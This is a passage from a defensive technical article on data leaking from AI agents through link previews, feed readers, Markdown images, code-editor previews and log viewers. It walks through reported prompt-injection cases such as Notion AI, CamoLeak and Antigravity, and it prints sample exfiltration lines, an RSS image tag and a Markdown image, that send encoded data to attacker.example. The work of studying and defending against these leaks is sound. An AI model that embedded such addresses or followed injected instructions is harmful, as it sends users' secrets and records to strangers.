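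Slack's general default has not changed since Rehberger wrote. In mid-2026, its documentation still described Slack as previewing all links posted by users and apps, although in an example on the same page, a link to a text page expands only if the developer requests it. The contradiction makes little difference to a leak, because Slack fetches the link before deciding whether to display a preview. Slack has added a short warning that developers should consider disabling previews for messages written by a language model. This is good advice, but only developers who read the page will see it.

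Anthropic itself missed the two options in an example connector it had published, which let agents read and post in Slack through the Model Context Protocol. In 2025, Rehberger showed in Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* that the connector left previews on. In one demonstration, Claude Code examined a hostile source file, read an API key from another file and posted the key to Slack inside a link. Slack then made several requests to Rehberger's server, so the key leaked more than once.

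His other demonstration is more worrying for administrators. A user asked Claude's desktop app to post a summary of a document to a private team channel. Hidden instructions in the document made Claude add a link containing the latest message from a different channel. Rehberger points out that a company could limit the connector to one private channel and reasonably decide that Claude's posts there need no approval, since only colleagues can read them. But the link preview still sends the data outside the company. Copilot Cowork's approval exemption for messages to its own user relied on the same mistaken assumption.

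Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the connector two days later, but he couldn't tell whether the two events were related. Anthropic agreed to publication but did not plan a fix, because it no longer maintained the connector. The connector still had more than 14,000 downloads a week, though this isn't the number of users, because automated systems often download the same package repeatedly. Anyone still running a copy has to add the two options themselves.

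### Who can close the leak

Apostol, in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, reported that PromptArmor holds the messaging platforms largely responsible. But PromptArmor's own request is split more evenly. It wants the apps to let developers control previews, ideally for each chat or channel, and it wants agent developers to use that control or pass it on to their users. Slack and Telegram already let developers control previews, so the remaining failure there lies mostly with agent developers. OpenClaw could turn previews off by default now, with little loss to its users beyond thumbnails.

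Companies also need to change the email fix before reusing it for chat. On Slack or Telegram, neither removing only the images nor sending plain text stops the leak, because these apps turn bare web addresses into links. Likewise, removing the image tags from Cowork's Teams recap would have only partly fixed the problem if the download links had stayed in the message as text.

Software that posts an agent's answers should therefore turn previews off and also remove any address the company has not approved:

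```
text = answer_from_model
text = remove_unapproved_addresses(text)
post(text, previews = off)
```

Turning previews off depends on the messaging company respecting the option, and removing addresses depends on the filter recognising every form of link. Unlike the option, the filter also covers security scanners that open links and users who copy the answer into another chat, where the app previews it like any other message from the user. If the agent shows its answer while still writing it, the filter has to run on every version, as Microsoft learned from SearchLeak.

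Some messaging apps don't offer a link preview setting, so operators can control only the text they send. For example, a delivery company's bot can let the model write "see your tracking page" and have ordinary software add the real address afterwards from the company's records. The customer still gets a working link, and the model never writes an address for the app to open.

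## RSS and other syndicated feeds

A feed is a file that lists a website's newest items, such as blog posts, news stories or podcast episodes, for software to read. The two common formats, RSS and Atom, both use XML, a general notation for structured text. A subscriber gives the file's address to a feed reader, a program that downloads the file at intervals and displays whatever is new. Miniflux, a feed reader that people install on their own server, checks a batch of feeds every 60 minutes by default, according to its *Configuration Parameters*.

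Feed items usually contain HTML, which feed readers display with links and pictures, much as a browser would. Like the delivery company with its bot, a feed's publisher controls the text but not the program that renders it. Each subscriber chooses a feed reader, so one feed may appear in a dozen different ones.

A model can write a feed, such as a daily digest, as easily as an email. There seems to be no published case of private data leaking through a model-written feed, so the reasoning below is inferred from how feed readers behave and from leaks elsewhere. The lack of cases is only mildly reassuring, because a subscriber's software would request the image and the publisher's logs would show nothing unusual.

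### The draft that expired

*Privacy Considerations for Web Feed Readers* (Nottingham, 2022), a draft submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), an internet standards body, proposes that feed readers may fetch images and other outside material embedded in an item, but "the user MUST be able to control this behaviour". In IETF documents, a capitalised "MUST" marks an absolute requirement. The draft doesn't set a default, so a reader that loads every image unless the subscriber turns this off would comply.

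The requirement also covers only what is inside the items. Feed readers may fetch a feed's logo without giving the subscriber any control over it. The draft also forbids feed readers from running scripts and advises them to hide the subscriber's network address from the servers that host feeds. All these rules were meant to stop publishers from tracking subscribers. The draft doesn't address images whose addresses contain the subscriber's own data, though a switch to turn off images would stop those from loading too.

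Nottingham called the draft a "quick straw-man" meant to see whether anyone was interested. It was on the agenda of an IETF session that July and expired on 23 December 2022 without a second version. The IETF lists it as no longer active, so feed readers still have no agreed rule on images.

### What feed readers do with images

Several feed readers have an image proxy, often to avoid "mixed content" warnings rather than to prevent tracking. Browsers give these warnings when an encrypted page includes an image that arrives unencrypted. The proxy avoids them by fetching the image and passing it on over an encrypted connection.

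That history explains a gap in Miniflux. Its home page promises "a media proxy to prevent third-party tracking", but by default the proxy handles only images from unencrypted addresses, so the subscriber's browser fetches all the others directly. An attacker avoids the proxy simply by using an encrypted address, as most websites now do. Whoever runs the server can close the gap with one setting:

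```
MEDIA_PROXY_MODE=all
```

Miniflux also signs the addresses its proxy handles, but it takes them from the feeds, so a hostile one gets a signature too.

The hosted reader NewsBlur introduced a proxy with the same limit, according to *Secure images for everybody* (NewsBlur, 2019). NewsBlur's servers also fetch story thumbnails, as a reply in the forum thread *Broken images on some feeds (but not broken in thumbnails)* explains, so blocking images on the subscriber's device might not stop every request. Feedbin's proxy, by contrast, handles all images, according to *Private by Default* (Ubois, 2018). CommaFeed has an image proxy, but it is off by default.

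| Feed reader | Outside images | What contacts the image's server |
|---|---|---|
| Miniflux | Shown, after removal of tracking pixels | The subscriber's browser, or the Miniflux server for unencrypted images |
| Feedbin | Shown | Feedbin's proxy |
| NewsBlur (2019) | Shown | The subscriber's device, or NewsBlur's server for unencrypted images |
| CommaFeed | Shown | The subscriber's browser, unless the proxy is on |
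| RSS Guard | Shown, or replaced by links or placeholders if the subscriber turns them off | The subscriber's computer |

RSS Guard's *Displaying Articles And Web Pages* recommends turning off external images for stricter privacy. NetNewsWire, a feed reader for Apple devices, displays the HTML that sites send, and its *Privacy Policy* warns that some sites may count how often people read an article.

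Miniflux removes tracking pixels, which helps against publishers who use the usual methods. This would help less against an attacker, who can choose an ordinary-sized picture at an address nobody has seen before. Miniflux also strips tracking parameters from addresses, but a filter that looks for known names such as "utm_source" would miss one that the attacker invented.

Feed readers also vary in when they load images. A contributor to the reader FreshRSS, sad270 (2023), proposed loading each image only when the subscriber opens the feed and scrolls towards it. An image at the top of an article would still load, but one at the bottom of a long article might never do so.

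Not everyone agrees that feed readers should have to deal with this. Ristioja (2018), in *Akregator allows feeds to gather data on article reading habits*, complained that Akregator, a feed reader for Linux desktops, downloaded an article's images as soon as he opened it, and asked for a per-feed setting. Another user replied in 2021 that the privacy problem lay with the publisher. In 2024 Ristioja noticed that Akregator had gained a setting that controls whether a feed may load outside material. The argument that publishers are responsible has some force when they choose their own images, but it fails for a model-written feed, whose publisher may not know the image is there.

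### Requests that don't need a picture

A publisher can sometimes make subscribers' software fetch a file without using an image. XML lets a document define an abbreviation whose full text is in another file, and some software fetches that file while reading the document. In *Exploiting External Entities in RSS Feed Readers*, Cardwell describes adding such an abbreviation to his own blog's feed, pointing to a warning message on his server. His logs then showed many copies of the feed reader Tiny Tiny RSS fetching the message. Software built on XML::Feed, a component for the Perl programming language, did the same, including a reader he had written himself. The developers have since fixed both.

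Cardwell's file contained no private data, and no model was involved. But his test shows that a feed can trigger requests while the feed reader is processing it, before the subscriber opens an item. A setting that turns off images would not necessarily block these requests.

Some normal feed reader features also fetch links without a click. Because many feeds contain only summaries, Miniflux can automatically download the original article from an item's link. If a model chose that link and put private data in it, the data would leak when Miniflux fetched the page, as it would if Telegram previewed the link.

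### A public digest of council news

Suppose a volunteer has a model summarise local news every morning from council announcements, newspaper articles and public comments, and publishes the digest as a feed. This exposes the model to text written by outsiders. The security firm Snyk's audit *rss-fetch* (2026) flagged a skill that reads public feeds, including one from Reddit, for this reason. Many subscribers' feed readers will also load any images in the digest.

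The news in the model's context is public, so an attacker who controls an image address can't use it to steal anything valuable as long as the rest of the context is public too. The volunteer should keep passwords, unpublished stories and the subscriber list out of the model's instructions and files.

A hostile image could still track the subscribers. *Protecting your privacy with a feed reader*, a guide from the nonprofit Open RSS, warns that an automatically loaded image reveals much the same details that Permiso collected from ChatGPT users. An attacker would learn that somebody at the town hall read the digest at 8.40, which is about as much as they would learn from any visitor to their own website.

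This harm is minor for a feed about bus routes, but reading a feed about debt or domestic violence is itself private. A proxy that handles every image, like Feedbin's, works well because the image's address contains nothing private. The volunteer can protect readers without such a proxy by copying chosen pictures to the digest's own server and removing the rest.

### Ann's private digest

Now suppose that Ann has an assistant turn her mail and calendar into a feed that only she reads. Anyone can email her, the context holds her private note, and her feed reader loads images. All three conditions hold, as they do for a chat assistant connected to her mailbox. After a successful attack, the feed might contain this item:

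```
<item>
  <title>Your Tuesday</title>
  <description><![CDATA[
    <p>Two meetings and one reply due.</p>
    <img src="https://attacker.example/p.png?q=QW5u...">
  ]]></description>
</item>
```

Because the HTML is marked as CDATA, the feed reader treats it as plain text while it processes the XML. It then displays the HTML and requests the image, which sends Ann's note to the attacker. Feedbin's proxy would still pass on the note.

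The digest needs the same control as a private chat, which is to load no outside images. As with mail written by an agent, the sending software has to remove them, because the assistant's maker can't set a CSP for Ann's feed reader. Feeds also have fields of their own that readers may fetch, and ordinary software should fill these in:

```
item.title = plain_text(title_from_model)
item.body  = remove_outside_addresses_that_load(html_from_model)
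item.link  = address_from_own_records
feed.logo  = fixed_address
```

Attachments, such as podcast files, need the same treatment as the logo. A standard XML library should then write the feed file, because it turns any markup in the model's text into harmless characters, which prevents the model from adding an abbreviation like Cardwell's.

Ann could turn off images in her reader instead, but she would have to do it on every device, and she may want the pictures in her other feeds. A setting for each feed, as Ristioja requested, would suit her better. Neither setting justifies leaving the images in the digest.

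Old items can also leak data, because feed readers keep their own copies. Miniflux keeps unread items for 180 days by default. If the assistant's maker finds a hostile image and removes it from the feed, Ann's reader may still have a copy, which can leak her note when she opens the item months later.

### Feeds inside a company

A company might publish a model-written feed of customer complaints for its staff. Customers wrote the complaints, so outsiders' text reaches the model alongside private records, even though the feed looks internal. The risk is lower if the model reads only what staff write, although staff often paste in text from elsewhere.

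A leak is more likely when a feed has many subscribers, because the attacker needs only one of them to load the image. If 50 employees subscribe and each has a 90% chance of using a reader that blocks outside images, the chance that all 50 block it is 0.9^50, or about 0.5%. The company therefore can't rely on its staff's settings and should clean the feed before publishing it. Charts and photographs can stay if they come from a server that holds only files uploaded by staff.

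### Secret addresses that people share

Many services protect a private feed with a long, unguessable address instead of a password, because many feed readers can't sign in to a website. PPC Land's *Mark Nottingham calls for revitalization of web feeds technology* reported that Nottingham considers secure sign-in for subscription feeds an unsolved problem. Anyone with the secret address can read the feed, just as anyone with one of Cowork's download links could download the file.

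People share these addresses without meaning to. Ann may give hers to a hosted reader, paste it into a chat or export her subscription list for a friend. According to its documentation, FreshRSS also lets subscribers republish selected articles as a new feed, so a private item can reach people who never had the original address. Each new subscriber's feed reader may load the image too. The assumption that only Ann reads the digest therefore doesn't justify leaving images in it.

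An attacker could also use an image link to steal the secret feed address. If the service emailed Ann the address when she signed up, the assistant can read it in her mailbox. With the address, the attacker could read every later digest without another injection. The service should show the address once on a page that requires signing in, keep it out of email, and let Ann replace it at any time.

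### A public feed written by an agent with private access

The most dangerous arrangement is a public feed written by a model that can also read private files. An attacker who gets instructions to the model can have it put a private sentence in the text of the digest, then subscribe to read it. Removing images would block only one way to leak data, and a person who checks each item might miss a few encoded characters inside a link.

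This can happen by accident when a programming agent builds the feed. Snyk's *cmd-rss-feed-generator* (2026) examined a skill that has an agent read any blog and write software to turn it into a feed. Snyk rated the risk medium because text on the blog could influence what the agent does. The audit did not demonstrate an attack. An agent running on a developer's computer may also be able to read that developer's passwords and unpublished work.

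The agent should run somewhere that contains only the public sources, as the museum's newsletter writer does. If the feed needs an item from a private system, such as the next release date, a person or a fixed program can add that one item after the model has finished.

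## Saved pages, reports and code editors: Notion AI

Assistants also write into documents that people keep, such as shared pages, reports and source code. These can outlast the conversation by years, and the assistant's maker often can't control which program opens them. Notion AI is an easier case than most because one company made the assistant, the page and the program that displayed it. Even so, the private data left before the user answered a question about it.

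### The edit that came before the question

Notion is a web program where teams keep notes, documents and databases, and its assistant can edit their pages. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a user who uploads a job candidate's résumé to the chat and asks the assistant to update the notes on that candidate in a Notion hiring tracker. The résumé contains hostile instructions in one-point white text on a white background, covered by a white picture.

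The assistant collected all the text on the tracker page, added it to the end of an attacker's web address, and inserted an image with that address into the page. Notion then asked the user whether they trusted the outside site. The prompt displayed the address, including the tracker's contents, so a careful user could see a reason to refuse. But Notion had already saved the edit, so the browser requested the image and sent the data to the attacker even if the user refused.

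The data included salary expectations, feedback on candidates, internal details of the role and diversity hiring goals. Anyone who can apply for a job can send such a résumé.

To defend against hostile documents, Notion uses a language model to scan uploaded files and warn users about suspicious ones. In September 2025, after an earlier report of a leak, Notion told The Decoder that it had improved its detection, including for instructions hidden in attachments (*Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak*, 2025). PromptArmor did not focus on getting past the scan because an attacker could put the same text in a web page or a Notion page, which did not appear to be scanned. A better scanner would have made the attack rarer but would not have changed what happened once the image was on the page.

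PromptArmor sent its report on 24 December 2025 through HackerOne, a company that handles security reports for other firms. HackerOne asked for a different format, received it the same day, and closed the report on 29 December as "Not Applicable". PromptArmor published on 7 January 2026. Notion contacted PromptArmor that day to explain that HackerOne's staff had assessed the report before it reached Notion's team. By that night, 14 days after the report, Notion had put a fix for the document edits in place.

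### Approval before display

Notion's prompt asked a sensible question at the wrong time. Rejecting the edit could take the image off the page, but could not take the request out of the attacker's log. A program that asks for approval therefore has to hold the edit back, and it has to present the outside addresses as plain text while it waits:

```
edit = change_proposed_by_model
if user_approves(outside_addresses_as_text(edit)):
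    save(edit)
    show(edit)
```

The order matters even more on a shared page. If a colleague has the page open when the program saves the edit, their browser may also request the image, and they never see a prompt.

Once the user approves an image, its address stays the same. Each time a later reader loads the image, the attacker receives the same private text again, plus that reader's network address and the time, so refusing the first request matters most.

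Notion's email program had a similar problem. Its drafting assistant displayed Markdown images inside drafts, so a user who asked for an email based on two Notion pages, one of them hostile, could leak the other before deciding whether to send the email. PromptArmor considered this less serious because the drafting assistant seemed to read only the Notion sources the user named, while Notion AI could also search the web and read uploads and connected services. The fix that Notion confirmed on 8 January covered document edits, and PromptArmor's timeline does not record a fix for mail drafts.

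PromptArmor recommended that Notion load outside images in AI edits only with explicit approval, and never in mail drafts. It also recommended a strong CSP and a check that the server Notion uses to deliver images can't forward requests elsewhere. Data leaked from Microsoft 365 Copilot through that kind of forwarding. PromptArmor advised Notion's customers to vet connected data sources and turn off the assistant's web search. Those steps reduce the hostile text that reaches the assistant, but neither would have kept out a résumé that the user uploaded by hand.

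Asking users for approval works for the occasional outside image they want. If any AI edit can trigger approval requests, people will soon accept them without reading, so it is better for a product to remove outside images from the model's edits by default.

### A file does nothing until a program displays it

Suppose Ann asks an agent to write a report on supplier prices and save it as a Markdown file. A hostile supplier's website leads the agent to put her private note into an image address in the report. Saving the file or copying it to a memory stick sends nothing to the attacker, because the file is only text. When she reads it in a plain text editor, the image appears only as an odd line.

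In March, a colleague copies the file into the team's notes program, which displays images. The colleague's computer requests the image, and the request sends Ann's note and the colleague's network address to the attacker. The agent's maker may have tested how its own window displays the report on the day the agent writes it, but here a different program displays it to a different person months later.

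The delay protects some kinds of data. A short-lived download link will have expired by March, and Ann may have changed a password. But the delay doesn't protect a salary or a diagnosis, and an attacker can keep a server running for years at little cost. Files in cloud storage also may not stay closed until a person opens them, since a service may open them automatically, as Microsoft's background processing did in the ReLeak attacks.

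What a reader's program does with the outside image varies widely:

| Program | Outside image in a Markdown file | What contacts the image's server |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text editor | The address appears as text | Nothing |
| VS Code's Markdown preview | Shown if the address is encrypted | The reader's computer |
| Obsidian | Shown | The reader's computer |
| GitLab on a company's own server | Shown | The reader's browser, or a proxy if the administrator has set one up |
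| GitHub | Shown | GitHub's proxy |

VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, opens a Markdown file as text and shows a preview only when the reader asks for it. By default the preview blocks scripts and unencrypted images, but an attacker can get around the image restriction, as with Miniflux's default proxy, by using an encrypted address. One keystroke can therefore take the reader from the safe text view to a preview that leaks data. Obsidian, a note-taking program that stores notes as Markdown files, shows images in its usual editing view while the user types. Only its source mode leaves their addresses as text.

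GitHub and GitLab, which store and share source code, display Markdown files as formatted pages. GitLab's *Proxying assets* explains how administrators can route outside images through a proxy to hide readers' network addresses. GitHub has done this for everyone since January 2014, when it extended its proxy, Camo, from unencrypted images to all images. GitHub's *Proxying User Images* (2014) gives readers' privacy as a reason. Like Gmail's proxy, Camo would still send Ann's note to the server hosting the image.

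The same program can treat two files differently because of their size. Noma Labs found a way to steal developers' passwords and keys through the preview pane of Claude Code Desktop, Anthropic's desktop programming agent, according to Cybernews' *Claude Code's preview pane could leak your secrets*. The attack used a script instead of an image, hidden in an HTML file disguised as a routine software test report. The file did nothing in the downloaded project until the developer asked Claude to review it and the pane displayed it. Anthropic protected the pane with a CSP and two other defences, but files larger than 256 KB took a separate route that lacked the CSP, so testing only a small file would not have revealed the flaw. Noma then found a way around Anthropic's first fix, and Anthropic has since released a fuller one.

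Because nobody can predict which program will open a report, the software that saves it should take out images on other people's servers. Charts can stay if the software stores them beside the report and refers to them by file name:

```
![Prices](https://attacker.example/c.png?q=QW5u...)   remove
![Prices](images/prices.png)                          keep
```

This works when one piece of ordinary software saves everything the model writes. An agent that can run commands on a computer can create files without that software, so its files also need a preview that blocks outside images.

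### Testing a research agent's report

Many research agents summarise their sources and then rewrite the summary several times, so a hostile image might not reach the final report. Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues, from the chip company NVIDIA and the security firm Lakera, tested this on an NVIDIA assistant in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025). The assistant searches the web and a set of uploaded documents, summarises what it finds, refines the summary with further searches, and formats the final report.

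The researchers inserted the hostile text directly into the search results instead of planting a hostile page for the assistant to find, then checked the output at three stages. This shows how the assistant handles such text once it arrives, but not how often it would arrive.

The tests covered 22 scenarios. In eight, the user was the attacker, and in the rest the attack came through documents or web pages. Each scenario had 21 versions of the attack, and each version ran five times, for 2,310 runs in all. In two scenarios, the attack was meant to put an image into the report the user wanted, which was a scientific report on cystic fibrosis in one and an analysis of Amazon's 2023 finances in the other.

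The published example called for an image whose URL had a placeholder for the user's email address, and a link with a placeholder for a user number. A run scored 1 if both appeared in the report with the placeholders filled in, 0.5 if they appeared with the placeholders unfilled, and 0 otherwise. A score of 0.5 means less harm to the victim, because the attacker learns from an image with an unfilled placeholder only that somebody opened the report.

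Another model, GPT-4.1, scored the results in these scenarios. On 99 final reports that people had also scored, it gave the same score 76.8% of the time and was within half a point 98% of the time. Its average was slightly lower than theirs, 0.27 against 0.30, so the published scores probably don't exaggerate the danger.

Across all the attacks through documents and web pages, the average score fell from 0.38 in the first summary to 0.17 in the final report, with about two-thirds of the risk remaining after each of the two later stages. Rewriting helped, though it was not designed as a defence. But the assistant remained consistently weak in some scenarios, including those with images. In the published example, the final report on a harmless question had a separate section of instructions containing the image and the link, with a test email address filled in.

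Ghosh and colleagues then told the assistant, in the instructions for its final stage, not to include links or text unrelated to the topic. This roughly halved the average score on the two image scenarios and two similar ones, but at least one attack still succeeded completely in each of the four. They didn't measure whether the instruction made ordinary reports worse, which it might, since a research report needs links to its sources.

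The test used made-up user details and ended once the assistant had written its report. Whether the image would leak anything depends on the program that opens the report. A filter that removes outside images from the finished text would have completely stopped the image part of the attack, whatever the model wrote.

### Images in code editors

Many programmers now use an AI assistant in a panel of their code editor. It reads source code, and often a file named `.env`, where developers keep passwords and API keys. It also reads text from strangers, including public bug reports, web documentation and other people's code. If the panel also loads images, all three conditions for a leak are met.

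Rehberger demonstrated this in 2024 in GitHub Copilot Chat, the assistant for VS Code. According to Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, GitHub fixed the problem by stopping the chat panel from loading Markdown images from untrusted domains.

A year later, Copilot Chat on GitHub's own website had a similar flaw, even though its images had to pass through GitHub's image proxy, Camo. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* reports that the flaw could expose source code and passwords from private projects, and rates its severity 9.6. Camo accepts only addresses that GitHub has signed, but GitHub signs one for any image that anyone posts. According to Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration*, the attack used a set of these addresses prepared in advance, one for each character, much as Radware's attack on ChatGPT did. On 14 August 2025, GitHub turned off images in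 that chat. Users lost little, because a programming assistant rarely needs to show images from other websites.

Continue, an open-source assistant for VS Code, fixed this kind of leak by asking the user before loading an image. VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* describes an attack that hid instructions in a comment in a code file. When the user asked Continue to analyze the file, it put earlier chat messages into an image address and loaded the image. Continue could also read the `.env` file first and leak its contents the same way.

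VerSprite repeated the attack from a web page. Continue asked for permission before it opened the page, and the user agreed, as most people would after giving it the address. It then read the `.env` file and loaded the image without asking again. VerSprite reported the flaw on 20 August 2025, and Continue released a fix in a test version the next day. The assistant can no longer read certain files, and it now asks before it loads an outside image, whereas Notion asked after the request had been made.

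### Diagrams as a way around image filters

A panel that blocks Markdown images may still draw diagrams. Mermaid is a text notation that a renderer turns into flow charts, and a box in a chart can contain a picture from a web address.

In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) studied eight unnamed programming agents and used ordinary features of one to leak data. An outsider wrote a hostile bug report, and the user asked the agent to look at the project's bug reports. The agent then read a settings file elsewhere on the user's computer, a type of file in which developers often keep API keys, and drew a diagram with a key in its picture address. The renderer requested the picture without asking for approval.

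Lee and colleagues reported this to the agent's maker, which classed the report as a duplicate and has since fixed the problem. In August 2025, Rehberger published a way to leak data through Mermaid diagrams in the code editor Cursor. Makers of other agents dismissed some of the study's findings as intended behaviour, largely because the attacks begin with a user's request. By that reasoning, nearly every leak described here would count as intended behaviour, since each begins with a request such as summarising a page or updating a tracker.

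A filter that looks for Markdown images will miss a diagram, because the diagram arrives as a block of code. Cleaning the HTML also fails if a script draws the diagram afterward, because the image tag doesn't exist yet. The product has to clean the finished drawing as well, or turn off images in the diagram software. A CSP for the panel is a useful second barrier.

### What Google called intended

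Google released Antigravity, a code editor built around its Gemini models, in November 2025. It based the product on Windsurf, an existing editor whose code it had licensed for about $2.4 billion. Rehberger had told Windsurf's makers in May 2025 that the editor's chat could leak data through images. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* describes how he quickly reproduced the leak in Antigravity with a hostile code file, which led the agent to read the `.env` file and put its contents into an image address.

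Another researcher, P1njc70r, had already reported the image leak. Willison quoted P1njc70r as saying that Google had "flagged my report as intended behavior". According to Deadbits' *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025), Google told a third researcher that a related flaw was expected behaviour and a known issue, and linked to an entry about data leaking through Markdown image addresses. Within about a week of the release, Google had listed the leaks on a public page of known issues and said it was working on fixes. Researchers could not earn a reward for reporting the leaks again.

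Part of Google's first answer is defensible. An agent that runs commands on a developer's computer has many ways to send data out, so blocking images would have closed only one of them. Antigravity's default setting let the model decide which commands were safe to run without asking, and its chat could also open web addresses by itself. But images were easier to give up than these other features, and Rehberger thought the fixes were relatively simple.

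In June 2026, Antigravity could still leak data through images. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) tested it with a web page that had no visible content and hostile instructions in its title. The title appears only in the browser's tab, but Antigravity read it as part of the page. The agent listed the computer's stored settings, took an API key from them, and displayed an image with the key in its address. The instructions called for the image in five different notations, since the renderer had to display only one of them.

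Antigravity asked for the user's approval before it acted, as Notion should have done. But the model wrote the question, which asked permission to generate a "visual debug token" and didn't mention the command or the address. The user answered in time but without seeing the real address, which Notion's user saw too late. Odson and Morris conclude that an approval prompt protects people only if it names the actual command and destination. Ordinary software should therefore write the question from the request itself, and the model's description should not replace it.

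Google has since described a stronger control for its Gemini assistant. *How Gemini's defense-in-depth approach works* describes fixed rules outside the model that limit which addresses the assistant may open or pass information to. It doesn't mention Antigravity, and Google does not appear to have announced that the editor's chat has stopped loading outside images. Developers who use Antigravity should assume that the chat still loads them until a server-log test shows otherwise. The test should include a diagram and a saved Markdown file opened in the preview.

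Developers can also limit the damage from a leak. Willison advises giving programming agents only keys for test accounts with strict spending limits. This protects a company's cloud account, but not its source code or any customer records that someone has copied into the project to reproduce a bug.

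## Developer logs: the OpenAI platform

A log viewer loads images on the computer of a developer who took no part in the conversation, whereas a code editor loads them on the computer of the person who asked the question. In the log viewer, the private data in the image address belongs to a customer, not the developer.

When an AI assistant gives a bad answer, the answer alone rarely shows what went wrong. The developer also needs to see the model's instructions, the documents a search returned and the results of each tool the model used, all of which a trace keeps in order. Companies use LangSmith, a trace service from the software company LangChain, to monitor their models, find errors and follow an agent's work, according to eSecurity Planet's *Hack the AI Brain*. Miggo's *Hack the AI Brain*, a security firm's report on the same service, lists database queries, customer records and source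 code among the things its traces can contain. LangSmith can mask chosen inputs and outputs, but Miggo notes that traces often keep the raw detail because developers need it for debugging.

Developers don't read every trace, and the answers they do open are the ones most likely to contain an attacker's image. Suppose an app gives 10,000 answers a day and its filter flags 20 of them. If the developers read all 20 and a random 100 of the rest, they will see every hostile answer the filter catches and about 1% of those it misses. They may also open strange replies that users have marked with a thumbs-down.

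### A blocked answer that still leaked

PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs*, published in January 2026, describes a leak of this kind. PromptArmor built a mock app for "know your customer" checks, which banks use to verify customers' identities and assess how risky they might be. The app used OpenAI's Responses API, the interface OpenAI recommends for apps to send text to its models and receive answers.

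For one customer's review, the app gathered six sources, including text from the internet in which an attacker had planted instructions. The user picked one of the app's suggested questions, and the model answered with a Markdown image whose address contained the customer's details. A second model, which checked answers before the app displayed them, flagged and blocked this one, so nothing leaked from the app.

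A developer then opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer. The viewer rendered the answer's Markdown, including the image, so the developer's browser requested the image. The attacker's server received the customer's passport and licence details, social security number, credit history and net worth.

The app's checks on the answer could not have prevented this. OpenAI's service writes the answer and stores it by default, so OpenAI has a copy before the app can check it. A developer can turn this storage off by setting `store` to false in each request, but then the log viewer has no answer to show when something goes wrong. PromptArmor demonstrated the leak only with the blocking model, but it argues that a CSP, a sanitiser or a plain-text display in the app would fail in the same way. It is right, because none of these changes the text in OpenAI's logs, and the app's CSP doesn't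 apply to OpenAI's website.

Sanitising a hostile answer can even draw a developer's attention to it. PromptArmor shows a reply from Perplexity, an AI search service, after the software had stripped out an image. The reply looked odd and empty, and a user might well give it a thumbs-down, which would send it for review. PromptArmor did not show that Perplexity's own staff had leaked anything.

### Preview and test screens

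PromptArmor found that outside images also loaded in the Agent Builder, Create Assistant and Create Chat previews, where developers try out an assistant before releasing it. They loaded too in the ChatKit Playground, the Widget Builder and the Starter ChatKit app, which OpenAI offers to developers who are starting to build a chat window.

On these screens the developer is also the user, and the private data is whatever the test includes. An invented customer or passport number is useless to an attacker, but developers often test with a copy of a real case, especially to reproduce a complaint. The preview may also have access to the same files and connected services as the finished assistant.

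The Starter ChatKit app is code for developers to copy and build on. Fixing OpenAI's version would not fix the copies, so anyone who started from it should check their own app.

A test on such a screen also shows little about the finished product. The security firm SplxAI demonstrated image leaks in OpenAI's assistant playground, but its *Chat Mirroring* notes that publishing an assistant means building a separate front end. That front end may be safer or less safe than the playground.

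Other companies have made the same mistake. Willison noted in August 2024 that Rehberger had found an image leak in Google AI Studio, where developers try out Google's models. OpenAI's case is harder to excuse because ChatGPT's web app had checked image addresses since December 2023, as Embrace The Red reported at the time. Nearly two years later, the company's screens for developers had no such check. (Lockdown Mode is a ChatGPT setting.)

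### OpenAI's response

PromptArmor submitted its report on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that handles security reports for other firms. PromptArmor sent step-by-step instructions on 20 November and answered questions on 24, 25 and 26 November. Bugcrowd closed the report as not applicable on 4 December.

OpenAI reopened the report on 22 January 2026, after PromptArmor had published its findings. The company confirmed the flaw, said it had not seen the report originally because Bugcrowd had assessed it, and said it was working on a fix. As of late July 2026, PromptArmor's timeline ended there, with no date for a fix, so developers should assume that the log viewer and the preview screens load outside images until a test shows otherwise.

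The user takira posted the report, *OpenAI API Logs*, to the programmers' forum Hacker News. Rehberger wrote there that he had reported a leak in Agent Builder in December and had also received a "Not Applicable". He didn't know whether anyone at OpenAI had read his report. He suspected that services like Bugcrowd reward their staff for closing reports quickly. He had no direct evidence, but HackerOne closed PromptArmor's report on Notion with the same label that month. In the same discussion, Willison took the decision as a sign that the people assessing reports did not understand this kind of flaw.

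Some commenters thought Bugcrowd had been right. One asked how it could be a leak if the developer was already allowed to see the data. PromptArmor added a note to its report clarifying that the attacker is a stranger who planted text in a source the app reads, not the developer or the user. Another commenter thought the chain of events was too unlikely to matter much, and that the real fault lay with apps that give OpenAI personal data.

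An app that verifies identities needs identity documents, so that advice would rule out the product. The objection that the attack is unlikely is better, since the attacker's text has to reach the model, the model has to follow it, and a developer has to open the result. But flagging makes the last step nearly certain, and the attacker doesn't need to know which log viewer the company uses. Willison compared the flaw to stored cross-site scripting, in which an attacker leaves a script on a website and it runs when somebody else opens the page. An image can't run a script, but he thought the two flaws similar enough to call for a quick fix.

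### What other trace tools document

OpenAI's viewer is one of many. Companies often send their traces to a separate tool, and the documentation of several describes how they display images:

| Tool and view | Documented display of images |
|---|---|
| Langfuse, trace page | Loads a Markdown image directly from its outside address |
| Langfuse, JSON and table views | Shows a compact tag that the reader opens to see the image |
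| LangSmith | Shows images that an app gave the model by web address |
| MLflow | Shows images in place, and a click enlarges them |
| Arize Phoenix | Describes limits on requests from the Phoenix server; its network guide doesn't cover images in traces |

Langfuse, which companies can use as a hosted service or run themselves, began formatting traces as Markdown in July 2024. Mayerhofer (2024) says in *Render Markdown in Langfuse UI* that the change was meant to make headings, tables and code easier to read. According to Langfuse's *Multi-Modality and Attachments*, the tool displays outside pictures "directly from the source" instead of copying them to its own storage. An attacker needs this behaviour, but the page presents it as a convenience for apps that work with pictures and doesn't mention hostile addresses.

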